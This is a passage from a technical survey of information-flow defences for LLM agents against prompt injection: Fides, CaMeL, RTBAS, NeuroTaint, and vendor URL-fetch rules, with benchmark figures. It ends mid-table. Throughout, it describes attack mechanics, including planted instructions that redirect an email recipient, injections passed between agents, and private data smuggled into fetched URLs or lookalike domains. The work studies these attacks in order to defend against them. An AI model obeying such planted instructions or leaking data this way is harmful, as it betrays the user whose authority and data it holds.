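The symbol `⊔`, pronounced "join", combines two labels, and here it selects the less trusted one. The calculation is the same for every argument of the call. Costa and colleagues use this rule in their simplest design and call it sound but possibly "overly conservative". In Garby and colleagues' language, a conversation carries the combined label of every message in it, so the untrusted page also makes all the model's later replies in that conversation untrusted. If the policy requires a trusted recipient, the adapter has to refuse the email to the manager even though it is correct.

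More careful record-keeping would not solve this because, as Wang and colleagues point out, showing whether a step depended on a passage takes an experiment, such as rerunning the step without it. That experiment covers only the passages that were present. Noninterference must hold for every possible page, and nobody can guarantee that for a model that reads the page before it writes the address.

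A system can guarantee that a web page doesn't influence an argument by controlling what the model reads. If the model writes a message's recipient before the page enters its input, the page can't alter the recipient. Costa and colleagues build on this idea in Fides, an agent design that can keep the page out of the main model's input. A policy can then require a trusted recipient while allowing the message to depend on untrusted text.

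For secrets, noninterference for the agent as a whole would roughly mean that an agent could not use any tool with publicly visible effects after using one that might read secret data. Some work aims instead for a weaker property, *explicit secrecy*, which requires that the steps the agent actually followed would have had the same public effects with different secret data. The choice of steps may still depend on the secrets, so someone who can watch the agent's calls may learn something from which tools it uses, their order, or a call that it omits.

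### Whether influence is harmful in itself

Letting the body depend on the page while protecting the recipient assumes that most influence is harmless. We can set out the argument for this as four premises:

1. The user asked for a summary of the page, so the body has to depend on the page. A defence that prevented all influence would also prevent the task.
2. What an agent can do with the user's authority depends on which tools it calls and what those calls reach, and therefore on the choice of tool and the sink arguments.
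3. If no page can change the tool or the sink arguments, an attacker can change only the content that goes to a destination the user chose.
4. Content that goes to a destination the user chose does no serious harm.

It would follow that a defence needs to control only the influence on the choice of tool and on the sink arguments.

The first premise is hard to dispute. The second doesn't cover harm from a call the agent never makes. The third is true only if the developer has identified every sink argument. The `city` argument in Semantic Kernel, for example, looked like harmless content until someone traced it to `eval`.

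The fourth premise is the weakest. Fan and colleagues describe a fraudulent payment request that does harm by reaching the right manager. Ameur and colleagues' guarantee likewise doesn't cover harmful text in a content field when it goes to an authorised destination. If the recipient is another agent, the email's body becomes untrusted text in that agent's input, and the attacker gets a second attempt, this time through that agent's different set of tools.

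Content can also do harm by revealing something the recipient should not see. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* describes violations in which every call matches the user's intent, but an argument carries sensitive data across a boundary. For example, a page might cause the model to add a line from a confidential email to the summary. Checking the origin of the recipient's address would not help, because the user gave that address. Costa and colleagues handle this with a separate policy that compares who may read the data with who will receive it.

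When a user asks for a summary of a page, the page should influence the summary through the facts it reports, not through a sentence that tells the model to praise the page's author. None of the three definitions separates these two kinds of influence, because the summary depends on both. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* proposes treating text inserted into a document as irrelevant to the task if it would not change the answer of a reasoner who made no mistakes. Self-promotion in a scientific paper is irrelevant in this sense because it does not change what the paper contributes. When an agent reviews papers, its verdict is a content argument, and an author who can sway the verdict does not need to change a sink argument.

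## Labels the runtime carries with each value

The most direct way to know where an argument came from is to label data when it enters the agent. Software outside the model assigns the labels, passes them on to anything the agent derives from the data, and checks them before a tool runs. An attacker can falsely claim on a web page that the user wrote it, but can't change the page's label, because the software that fetched the page assigned it.

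The model complicates the second step because all its output gets the combined label of everything it has read. Designs such as Fides, CaMeL and RTBAS differ mainly in how they keep that label from blocking useful work.

### Combining labels

A *lattice* is a set of labels with an order, `⊑` ("may flow to"), and a rule for combining any two labels. The simplest integrity lattice has two labels, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. Trusted data may go anywhere that accepts untrusted data, but untrusted data may not go where a tool requires trusted data. The simplest confidentiality lattice has public ⊑ secret. The combining rule, called the *join* (`⊔`), gives the least restrictive label that both labels may flow to, so public joined with secret is secret.

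Costa and colleagues also describe finer labels that name people. A confidentiality label can be the set of people who may read a piece of data. The join of two such labels is the intersection of the sets, since only someone who may read both sources may read a text based on both. An integrity label can be the set of people who could have written the data, and the join is the union.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example in which nobody attacks anyone. Alex asks an agent to answer the unanswered emails in an inbox. One is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales, and another is from Marco, who would like to know the sales figures but may not see them yet. After the agent has read both emails, any reply it writes has this label:

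```
{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}
```

Marco is not in the set, so the agent must ask before sending him the reply. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the label would have been {Alex, Marco} and the agent could have sent the reply without asking.

A complete label has one part for integrity and one for confidentiality, and the join combines each part separately. Costa and colleagues give a basic policy for each. The integrity policy allows a consequential call, such as a payment, only if the call's label is trusted. The confidentiality policy allows a call that sends data only if everyone who will receive the data may read it. This limits what a prompt injection can leak but does not prevent the injection.

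A policy can also allow a call that passes either an integrity check or a confidentiality check. Microsoft's sample policy for a chat tool allows a message if no untrusted data influenced the call, or if every member of the channel may read the content. Otherwise, the user decides. A user can therefore share a confidential figure on purpose, but a web page can't make the agent leak it without the user's approval.

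### How one page marks the whole conversation

For the email to the manager, the labels develop like this. The second part of each pair says who may read the data.

```
user's request               (trusted, anyone)
call that fetches the page   (trusted, anyone)
page                         (untrusted, anyone)
context after the page       (trusted, anyone) ⊔ (untrusted, anyone)
                             = (untrusted, anyone)
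recipient, subject, body     (untrusted, anyone)
```

Only the first call is trusted, because the model generated it before the page entered its context. A policy that requires a trusted recipient would block even the correct email.

If the user next asks the agent to book a meeting room, the booking is untrusted too. Costa and colleagues measured the effect on AgentDojo's Slack tasks with GPT-4o. An ordinary agent that was not under attack completed 93% of the tasks without policy checks and 20% with the checks.

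### Keeping the page out of the main model's input

Fides, the design by Costa and colleagues, avoids this by withholding the page from the model that writes the calls. When a tool returns a result, the runtime compares each part's label with the conversation's label. If adding a part would raise the conversation's label, the runtime stores that part in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model still sees the trusted parts, which help it decide what to do next.

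The model can pass a variable to a tool without reading it. To summarise the page, it passes the variable to a *quarantined model*, a separate language model that has no tools and returns its answer in another variable. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed this division of work. The email task then becomes:

```
#page    = fetch_page(...)                          untrusted
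#summary = query_llm("Summarise this page", #page)  untrusted

send_email(
    recipient = "manager@company.com",              trusted
    subject   = "Summary of the page",              trusted
    body      = #summary                            untrusted
)
```

Just before the call, the runtime replaces `#summary` with the text and keeps the variable's own label, so only the body is untrusted. The subject line is vaguer because nothing in the main model's input shows that the page is about customs rules.

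Quarantine does not clean the data. An instruction on the page could still make the quarantined model return a false or empty summary. *SPA* (2026), a related design, states the labelling rule for such a step:

```
label(output) = pc ⊔ label(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(xₙ)
```

The `x` values are the step's inputs, and `pc` is the label of the condition that led the program to this step. The output is thus never more trusted than the inputs.

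Sometimes the main model needs information from the hidden data. In Costa and colleagues' example, a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if it finds one. Fides lets the main model query the quarantined model for a yes-or-no answer, because revealing the emails to itself with the `inspect` tool would make the conversation untrusted. Constrained decoding, which blocks tokens that don't fit a given format, guarantees that the answer is yes or no. The main model inspects only that answer. If it is yes, the main model has the quarantined model extract the meeting's details into a variable, then passes the variable to the calendar tool.

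To let policies tell such answers apart from free text, Fides adds a type to each label, ordered by how much information a value can carry:

```
yes/no ⊑ choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text
```

A policy that accepts untrusted yes-or-no answers makes a deliberate exception for values of the smallest type. Garby and colleagues object that such exceptions are hard to audit. On a given run, a reviewer can't tell whether an admitted value is the harmless case the developer had in mind or a real leak. The exception also covers only the decision to create the event. The date and guest list still come from the email, so its author chooses them.

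### What Fides guarantees and what it costs

Costa and colleagues use a formal model of the agent's loop to work out which properties label tracking at run time can enforce. One kind is a *safety* policy, a rule that software can check against the steps taken so far, such as a ban on sending mail after opening a payroll file. The other is explicit secrecy, the weaker alternative to noninterference. Let `g` be the combined effect on stored data of the calls the agent actually made. The property is then:

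```
if d₁ =L d₂, then g(d₁) =L g(d₂)
```

Here `d₁` and `d₂` are two possible states of the stored data, and `=L` means they agree on everything public. Suppose the agent reads a salary, then sends a fixed greeting to Amira if the salary is high or to Ben if it is low. On either path, the greeting would be the same whatever the salary, so explicit secrecy holds, but anyone who sees who received it still learns whether the salary is high. The model also treats the language model as deterministic and leaves out side channels such as timing.

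The experiments used AgentDojo, GPT-4o and an attack in which the planted text names the tools to call. The table shows the share of tasks each agent completed without an attack. The last column shows the number of successful attacks in separate runs. The "variables only" agent hides untrusted results but has no quarantined model and cannot inspect variables.

| Agent | Policy checks | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
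|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | off | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% | 152 |
| Ordinary | on | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% | 0 |
| Variables only | on | 48% | 44% | 56% | 35% | 0 |
| Fides | off | 64% | 50% | 65% | 64% | 21 |
| Fides | on | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% | 0 |

With the checks on, every agent stopped every attack, so the designs differ only in how many tasks they complete. Averaged over the four applications, Fides completed about 8 percentage points more than the ordinary agent with checks. It did worse on travel, where the policies let many tools run after the agent had read untrusted text, so hiding that text brought no benefit and gave GPT-4o more chances to confuse variable names. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, Fides completed 68% of the travel tasks and its average lead grew to 16 points.

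The drop is much larger when compared with an ordinary agent with no protection. With GPT-4o, the average falls from 84% to 50%, and some of that loss is due to the model's mistakes rather than the policies.

The zeros in the last column reflect a manual review. AgentDojo counted three successful attacks against Fides with policy checks, and Costa and colleagues removed them after inspecting each one by hand. Across the agents, the cases they removed included calls that the policy had blocked, messages that the policy allowed, and attacks that changed only the wording of a text. The policies did not check tool arguments, and the experiments did not use constrained decoding. The labels were also unusually good, because the researchers marked as untrusted every data field that any AgentDojo attack uses. Someone who deploys Fides has no such list and must work out which fields an outsider can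 write to.

### A program written before the data arrives

In Fides, the main model chooses each call after seeing the results of the previous ones, with the untrusted parts hidden. CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and others introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), asks the main model for the whole plan at once. The model sees only the user's request and the descriptions of the tools, and it writes a program in a restricted form of Python:

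```python
page = fetch_page("...")
summary = query_quarantined_llm("Summarise this page", page)
send_email(
    recipient="manager@company.com",
    subject="Summary of the page",
    body=summary,
)
```

CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter, one operation at a time, and records which values each new value depends on. Here `summary` depends on `page`, whereas the recipient is a fixed string that the main model wrote before the program fetched the page. Each value also has *capabilities*, tags that record its source and who may read it. Before every tool call, the interpreter checks the arguments' tags and dependencies against that tool's policy.

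CaMeL adds these records to Willison's two-model pattern. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the weakness they address. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The plan is fixed, so the notes cannot add a tool call. But the quarantined model reads the address from the notes, and a planted instruction can make it return the attacker's address instead, so the planned call sends the document to the wrong person. CaMeL's interpreter records that the address depends on the notes, so a policy can block the call or require the user's approval.

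The CaMeL paper lists the need to write and maintain those policies among the system's limits. It also describes the risk that people who must approve many actions start to approve everything.

Measurements of CaMeL's usefulness vary with the set-up. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran the released code on AgentDojo through an adapter. None of 629 attacks succeeded, but with no attack CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks, while SecureClaw, a rival system from the same study, completed 59. This comparison may not show CaMeL at its best, because a competitor ran it and CaMeL needs careful preparation. CaMeL's main model has to write code to read a tool's output before seeing any of that output, so the tool descriptions must specify its exact format, and AgentDojo's do not. Policies reduce the score further. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL completed half as many of AgentDojo's banking tasks with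 its policy checks on as with them off.

The interpreter can record dependencies only inside the program it runs. Besides the leak through branches that the program does not take, Garby and colleagues found another outside the interpreter, in the ordinary Python loop that restarts the program after a failure. If a policy blocks a call only when some secret condition is true, the failure reveals one bit, and repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret.

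To close such gaps, Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in their own programming language, where every value has a label and any decision to raise a value's trust appears explicitly in the program. Randori completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks off, even though Randori's tracking was always on. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs.

### CaMeL with several agents

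Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, found that using one agent as another's tool can defeat CaMeL, even if every agent runs it. They built a system in which a coordinating agent delegates work to a database agent and a notification agent. They asked it to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack, with an instruction planted in the database. The coordinator's program inserted the summary into a sentence asking the notification agent to send it. The notification agent treated that whole sentence as the user's request, so its main model read the planted instruction as trusted text and planned an extra email to the attacker.

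Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering*. They also prove that if at least one tool returns untrusted data and the agents can carry out a reasonable range of requests, some request will let that data change another agent's plan, or the same agent's plan on a second call.

Multi-CaMeL, an extension of CaMeL, splits each message between agents into instructions and variables. The interpreter rejects the instructions if they depend on any tool's output. The variables keep their labels, and the receiving agent's main model never reads them. In tests on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, with 949 attacked cases for each of five models, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent ran ordinary CaMeL, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL.

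GPT-5.5 resisted every attack with no defence, so these attacks are too weak to show much about the newest models. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL without any policies on arguments, so their result covers attacks that change the plan but does not test whether a page could supply a false recipient to a call already in the plan. Multi-CaMeL also uses CaMeL's interpreter, so it too fails to account for branches not taken.

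### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

*Learning to Inject* (2026), a study of automated attacks, argues that defences with a fixed plan sacrifice the flexibility that makes agents useful. An agent often opens a file and finds it needs another one, or gets no results from a search and tries different words. A program written in advance can adapt like this only if its author anticipated the situation.

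The evidence supports the objection. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most of CaMeL's task failures, with or without their extension, occurred because the model had committed to a plan before seeing the data. In other cases, an agent could not find data for the period the user had requested and returned data for a nearby period instead, and the calling program continued with the wrong figures.

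On 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark about maintaining industrial equipment, ordinary CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points over five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for those two. Stronger models evidently write plans that cover more cases, but 13 points is still a substantial loss.

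How often the problem arises depends on the type of task. Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks by whether a single sequence of calls would work for any data the agent might find. By their percentages, 20 of the 97 tasks have no such sequence, including 9 of the 21 Slack tasks and 2 of the 40 office tasks. Even for those 20, a program with an `if` statement may be enough when the alternatives are predictable.

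Fides can handle some of the unpredictable cases because it plans again after every result, but this uses many tokens. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapted CaMeL and Fides to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The token overhead was 1.88 times for the CaMeL version and 29.6 times for the Fides version, which sends the main model the full history at every step.

Planning doesn't help when the user wants the agent to follow instructions in untrusted text. Several of AgentDojo's banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, such as scheduling a payment. Fides refuses, and Costa and colleagues count the refusal as intended behaviour. The labels alone can't distinguish the bill the user wants to pay from a forged one. The agent has to ask the user, or the policy has to specify what the user delegated and to whom.

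### Labelling only the relevant context

Another way to limit the spread of labels is to keep the ordinary agent loop and ignore any text that the next step does not need. Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, divide the conversation into regions, each with its own label. Before the model writes its next message, the system goes through these steps:

1. A *screener* judges which regions the message will depend on.
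2. The runtime joins the labels of those regions.
3. It removes every region whose label may not flow to the result.
4. The model writes the message from what remains.
5. If the message is a tool call whose policy does not permit the joined label, the runtime asks the user to confirm it.

Suppose the user asks for a meeting room after the agent has read the customs page. The screener classifies the page as irrelevant, and the runtime removes it before the model writes the booking. Trusting the booking is then justified because the page was not in the model's input.

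Because of the third step, a mistake by the screener may cause inconvenience but doesn't weaken security. If the screener wrongly includes the page, the user gets an unnecessary question, and if it wrongly leaves the page out, the model lacks information it needed. Even if an attacker writes a page that fools the screener, the page is either absent from the model's input or reflected in the label.

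Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One is a second language model that reads the conversation with its regions marked and lists the ones that matter. The other has the agent write a draft, then uses a small open model's attention weights to compute how strongly the draft depends on each region. A small neural network turns these scores into a decision for each region, and its decisions were right 81% of the time on test data.

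In tests with GPT-4o on AgentDojo's 629 attacked cases, both versions stopped every attack that violated the policy. Compared with an undefended agent under the same attacks, the version that uses a language model as screener lost less than 1% of its utility, and the attention version lost 3%. Without attacks, they lost 10% and 7.4%, respectively. One planted instruction was in a text that the user had supposedly written, so the system labeled it as trusted and did not track it.

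The first version completed only 22% of the Slack tasks, and the second only 33%. Many of these tasks involve reading a website and posting about it, and RTBAS gives a whole message one label. The email to the manager has the same problem, since the page is relevant to the body, so the recipient becomes untrusted too and the user has to confirm a correct call. The system refused such calls outright in these tests, and more tasks would have been completed if a user could have approved them.

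Zhong and colleagues wrote 37 tasks involving private data, such as card numbers, to measure how often RTBAS would interrupt users. A system that asks the user before every call did so needlessly in 30% of the tasks, compared with 8% for the language-model screener and 16% for the attention screener. Both screeners roughly doubled the price and running time of the banking tasks. The researchers estimate that an earlier method, which reran the model on different subsets of its input, would typically need 16 to 64 extra model calls.

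### Fides in Microsoft's Agent Framework

Microsoft released a version of Fides in May 2026 as part of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes it as *middleware*, code that runs before and after every tool call. Fides keeps a label for the conversation that records its integrity as trusted or untrusted and its confidentiality as public, private or user identity. The user identity level covers personal data and passwords.

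Developers switch it on with one configuration object. By default, it then hides untrusted results in variables, blocks calls that violate a policy and records them in a log. It can also ask the user about a violation instead of blocking the call. But it knows nothing about the tools, so developers have to declare several things:

- For a tool that reads data, the label of each item it returns, or one integrity label for everything it returns.
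- For a tool that acts, whether it accepts untrusted data and the highest level of confidentiality it may handle.
- Which tools, such as those that fetch web pages, may run even when the conversation is already untrusted.
- Which model to use for quarantine. Without one, the quarantine tool returns only placeholder text.

The release post and Microsoft's documentation differ on what happens when a developer forgets to label a tool that reads data. In the release post, the tool's output is treated as trusted and public, so a forgotten label on a web-fetching tool would remove the protection against injection. In the documentation, the default is untrusted and public, and the recommendation is to change it only for a closed set of fully vetted tools. Developers can avoid the uncertainty by setting the default themselves. Unlabelled output is public in both accounts, so a forgotten label on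 a tool that reads private files would let their contents leave through any tool.

The released version is also coarser than the research design. A developer declares whether a whole tool accepts untrusted data, so they cannot require a trusted recipient while accepting an untrusted body. In the release post's example, a tool that writes files will not run if either the path or the content comes from an untrusted source. Microsoft has a separate prototype, for tools that use the Model Context Protocol, that labels individual arguments and lets policies refer to a single argument.

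GitHub's command-line coding assistant, Copilot CLI, has experimental support for the same labels, but only for some tools so far. GitHub's tool server labels content from public repositories as untrusted and public, and content from private ones as trusted and private. This rule is practical, but an outsider's text becomes trusted as soon as an employee pastes it into a private repository.

Microsoft calls the Agent Framework feature experimental, and its documentation lists it for Python only. Microsoft has continued to develop it since May. Releasebot's *Agent Framework Updates & Release Notes* (2026) reproduces the 13 November notes for version 1.26.0, which include several fixes to how labels are kept when an application saves and reloads a conversation. The module now treats reloaded messages without a valid stamp cautiously, and it rejects a saved history that has changed or is partly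 missing.

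## Matching argument values to text in the context

Fides, CaMeL and RTBAS track data while the agent works, so they have to control what its model reads. A simpler approach leaves the agent alone. Software keeps a copy of every text the model receives, with a note of its source, and waits for the model to write a tool call. It then searches the copies for each argument's value:

```
origins(a) = every source s for which match(a, s) is true
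```

If `a` is manager@company.com and the user's message contains that address, the software infers that the user supplied the recipient. But a match only shows where the model could have found the value. The same address may also be on the page, and the call doesn't record which copy the model used.

A check can use matches in a *permission rule*, which accepts a value only if a trusted source contains it, or an *alarm rule*, which refuses a value if an untrusted source contains it. Either rule stops the email to the stranger. The alarm rule has the same weaknesses as any content test. It blocks the correct email if the customs page also lists the manager's address, and it may miss the stranger's address if the page contains it in a disguised form. The permission rule decides both cases correctly, but it would block a Slack invitation to Dora that uses the address from her website.

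The rule determines which matching errors are dangerous. Under a permission rule, a false match can let an attacker's value through, while a missed match only blocks a legitimate call. These effects are reversed under an alarm rule. Looser matching therefore makes an alarm rule safer but a permission rule less safe.

### Exact matching

The strictest test is an exact string match, and its reliability depends on how likely the string was to appear by chance. An email address or a long account number rarely occurs in two unrelated texts. But the number 2 or the word "yes" could appear in many of the texts an agent reads, so finding it in the user's message is weak evidence that the argument came from there.

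The software also has to compare complete values. A plain text search for ann@company.com finds a match inside joann@company.com, so a request that contains Joann's address would appear to authorise an email to Ann. Even a correct match doesn't show why the value was there. If the user writes "don't copy ben@company.com on this", Ben's address is in trusted text and passes the check.

Exact matching misses any value that the model had to work out. For example, a user who asks for a meeting "the day after tomorrow" doesn't write the date used in the calendar call, and someone who asks to pay half a bill doesn't write the amount.

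Cai and colleagues' auditing tool, NeuroTaint, makes accidental matches almost impossible. It adds a unique random marker, called a *canary*, to the text that a source returns, and later looks for the marker in the arguments. They report no false alarms from this test. But the marker reaches an argument only if the model copies it along with the surrounding text. If the model takes just an email address from the page, the argument won't contain the marker. They also write that a marker at the end of a document survives most summaries that cut off the end, which seems backwards, since the cut would remove the marker too.

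### Different spellings of the same value

Two different strings can name the same thing. *Normalisation* converts both to a standard form before comparing them, which finds matches that an exact comparison would miss. It is safe only if the program that finally uses the value also treats the two strings as the same.

| Difference | Example | Same destination? |
|---|---|---|
| Accented letter stored as one character or as a letter plus an accent | é | Usually, but some file systems keep two separate files |
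| Capital letters in a domain name | Company.com, company.com | Yes |
| Capital letters in the rest of a web address | /Report, /report | Depends on the server |
| Percent-encoded letter | %61, a | Yes |
| Percent-encoded slash | %2F, / | Not always, because a plain slash separates parts of a path |
| Letter from another alphabet | Cyrillic а, Latin a | No |

Percent-encoding represents a character in a web address as a percent sign followed by a number. Decoding the address once makes its ordinary letters comparable with unencoded text, but decoding a slash can split one part of the path into two.

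A checker should merge lookalike letters when it applies an alarm rule but not when it applies a permission rule. Anthropic gives the example of amazon.com spelled with a Cyrillic first letter, which looks the same to a person but is a different domain. Standard Unicode normalisation does not merge the two letters, but a table of lookalikes can. An alarm rule that used such a table would catch more disguised values, while a permission rule that used it would accept the fake domain because the user had mentioned the real one. It is better to refuse a domain that matches a trusted one only after lookalikes are merged. NeuroTaint excludes lookalike characters from its threat model.

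Anthropic also warns that programs may normalise Unicode in web addresses differently. As a result, the checker can approve one address while the fetching tool opens another. The adapter can avoid this by parsing the address once, checking the result and passing that same result to the tool.

### Similar wording and similar meaning

Normalisation does not help when the model has rewritten the source. NeuroTaint first looks for partial overlap with this score:

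```
overlap = |LCS(source, argument)| / min(|source|, |argument|)
```

LCS is the longest common subsequence, the longest series of items that occurs in both texts in the same order, possibly with gaps. Cai and colleagues report a match if the score is at least 0.15, a threshold they set low because arguments are often short. How strict this threshold is depends on whether the items are characters or words. If they are characters, any three in the right order are enough to match the 19 characters of manager@company.com, so the "com" in almost any web address produces a match. If they are words, the email address is a single item that either matches or doesn't.

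The next test compares meaning. A small language model called all-MiniLM-L6-v2 converts each text into an *embedding*, a list of numbers arranged so that texts with similar meanings get similar lists. NeuroTaint computes the cosine of the angle between the two lists:

```
similarity = e(source) · e(argument) / (‖e(source)‖ ‖e(argument)‖)
```

NeuroTaint scores the similarity between an argument and a source text. It normally counts a score of at least 0.60 as a match, but requires 0.85 for text retrieved from memory or a document store. The score can connect a summary to its source even if they share no phrases. When a planted sentence is a small part of a long page, the rest of the page lowers the score, so NeuroTaint also divides the source into chunks of a few sentences and compares each chunk with the argument.

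The drawback is that two texts on the same subject can match even when neither came from the other. For example, a memo about customs rules that the model wrote from general knowledge will resemble any page about customs rules.

Similarity of meaning is also a poor test for most sink arguments. Two email addresses that differ by one letter may have very similar embeddings but belong to different people. To show the value of comparing meanings, Cai and colleagues give an example in which a page contains an instruction to forward all mail to an archive address, and the model rewrites this as advice to copy in an archiving service. But the address stays the same, so an exact search would have found it. Comparing meanings is more useful for the body of an email, where an auditor may want to trace the rewritten material.

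### Web addresses that an agent may open

This kind of matching is most visibly used on web addresses. When an agent fetches a page, it sends the address to a server, and servers commonly record requested addresses. An attacker could therefore plant an instruction telling the model to write private data into an address and open it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that this can happen in the background, for example when the agent loads an image, so the user may never notice.

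Anthropic's web fetch tool opens an address only if it has already appeared in the conversation. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, the Chinese edition of the tool's current documentation, lists three places that count:

- the user's messages
- results from the developer's own tools, which Anthropic calls client-side tools
- earlier results from Anthropic's web search or web fetch

If the model requests an address that appears only in its own output, the system prompt, or results from Anthropic's code execution tool, it receives an error instead of the page.

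Under the second item on the list, an address that the model composed can count as one that it read. Suppose a developer provides a tool that runs code and returns whatever the code prints. The model can write code that prints an address, and the tool's output will then contain that address. An error message that quotes the model's input has the same effect. By default, Anthropic accepts addresses from such results.

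Developers can close the gap with an option called `url_sources`. It has a separate setting for each of the three places, and can also exclude individual tools:

```json
"url_sources": {
  "client_tool_results": {
    "type": "except",
    "tools": [{"type": "tool_reference", "name": "run_code"}]
  }
}
```

This setting rejects addresses that appear only in the output of `run_code`. If the developer later adds another tool, its output counts automatically. If `except` is changed to `only`, the output of the named tools counts and the output of new ones does not. `only` is therefore safer for a developer who expects to add tools and might forget to update this setting.

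Anthropic has a stricter rule for passwords and keys inside an address. The tool refuses an address that seems to contain one unless the credential appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. The address itself may come from a tool result, but a credential that appears only there does not count, so one argument can have two origin requirements.

The default is narrower in Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running agents. The service adopted the rule on 7 October, according to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026). Its agents cannot open an address from an attached document, from the tools that run shell commands and read files, or from tools connected through the Model Context Protocol unless the developer sends that address in a user message.

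The rule prevents the model from composing an address of its own, but an address that passes may still be untrustworthy. An attacker can publish a page containing any link, and once the agent fetches the page, that link has appeared in the conversation. Willison (2025) considered a list of permitted domains much stronger protection, although he called it tricky to find domains that nobody could use to extract data. Anthropic's tool also supports such lists.

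### Whether the address was already public

OpenAI looked for a different rule partly because domain lists have two weaknesses. A link on a trusted site can redirect to another site, and a strict list produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them. (In Managed Agents, Anthropic has addressed redirects by requiring an address reached through one to pass the domain lists as well.)

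OpenAI's safeguard, described in January 2026, compares the exact address with an index built by a crawler. The crawler explores the public web like a search engine and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the crawler has already recorded the address, the agent may open it automatically. Otherwise, OpenAI treats the address as unverified and either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

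Both companies compare an argument with a collection of known strings, but the collections support different conclusions. Anthropic's rule concerns where the address came from. OpenAI's concerns whether the address could contain the user's private data, which is unlikely if it was on the public web independently of the user. The difference shows in particular cases, here with Anthropic's default settings and no domain lists:

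| Address | Anthropic | OpenAI |
|---|---|---|
| A public page the model remembers from training | Refuses | Opens, if indexed |
| A private sharing link the user pasted | Opens | Treats as unverified |
| A new link on an attacker's page the agent has read | Opens | Treats as unverified until indexed |
| An address the model composes from private data | Refuses, unless a tool repeats it | Treats as unverified |

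OpenAI's rule is better matched to the risk of data leaks because it applies to the address itself. Anthropic's rule doesn't require an index of the web, and it doesn't interrupt users who want the agent to read a private link.

Both rules still allow some information to leak, because the agent chooses which permitted address to open. As with the choice between approved contacts, one request that an outsider can see conveys at most log₂ *N* bits when *N* addresses are permitted. With 1,024 addresses, that is 10 bits, enough for a three-digit number. Anthropic's rule permits addresses in the conversation, and OpenAI's permits addresses in the index. Several requests can convey more, so capping the number of fetches also limits the leak.

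Even so, both rules reduce the leak greatly. Anthropic's tool accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. A model free to choose every character from an alphabet of 64 could put up to 1,500 bits into one address.

OpenAI notes that its check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy. An address can pass either rule and still lead to a page that contains planted instructions. An earlier version of Anthropic's documentation warned of "residual risk" and recommended using the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data.

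### How NeuroTaint traces a value

Web addresses suit exact matching because they are long and the model has to reproduce them accurately. NeuroTaint, which Cai and colleagues introduced in April 2026, is designed to trace arguments of every kind. It is an *auditor*, meaning it analyses the record of a run after the agent has finished.

NeuroTaint's policy file lists which tools are sources, such as web search, and which are sinks, such as sending mail. While the agent runs, NeuroTaint records each tool call in a *provenance graph*. Each node is a call, with its arguments, session and any taint labels. Each edge records a label that passed from one call to another, the test that found the connection and a confidence score.

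The graph also covers memory. When the agent saves a note, NeuroTaint stores the labels next to it, and at the end of the session it saves the whole graph to disk. In one test case, the agent saves a confidential revenue forecast, and three days later a user asks it to write an operations report. When the agent retrieves the note, NeuroTaint restores the label from the first session. Reading a note may be harmless, so NeuroTaint raises an alarm only if the forecast appears in the report or affects whether the agent writes it.

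For each sink call, NeuroTaint tests every source connected to the call in the graph. It runs the tests in order of how much computation they need: canary, partial overlap, similarity of meaning, and comparison with chunks of the source. If all four fail, it tests for counterfactual influence by asking a language model whether the agent would have made the same call if neutral text had replaced the source.

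The judging model reads two versions of the conversation and predicts what the agent would have done, but the prediction isn't tested by running the agent. The confidence score is also the model's own estimate. The judge reads any planted instructions too, so they could influence its verdict. AgentDojo avoids language-model judges because of this risk.

### What TaintBench measured

To test NeuroTaint, Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios, 20 for each of 20 open-source agent frameworks. In 200 scenarios, untrusted text should reach or influence a sink call. The other 200 have no such flow, although most of them still contain both a source and a sink. Two of the researchers independently reviewed every scenario, and the team fixed the labels before comparing any detectors. The main experiment used GPT-4.1 mini as the agent. Each scenario ran five times, and three alarms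 counted as a detection.

*Precision* is the share of alarms that are correct, *recall* is the share of real flows that cause an alarm, and F1 combines them:

```
F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)
```

NeuroTaint had a precision of 0.921, a recall of 0.935 and an F1 of 0.928. Fides, which Cai and colleagues used for comparison, had an F1 of 0.522. The table shows where the alarms occurred.

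| Type of scenario | Scenarios | NeuroTaint alarms | Fides alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Flow present** | | | |
| Copied markers or strings | 60 | 60 | 45 |
| Material spread over several fragments | 15 | 15 | 6 |
| Material rewritten several times | 42 | 35 | 31 |
| Material passed through memory or another agent | 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Influence only on the agent's decision | 40 | 37 | 17 |
| Other | 13 | 12 | 4 |
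| **No flow** | | | |
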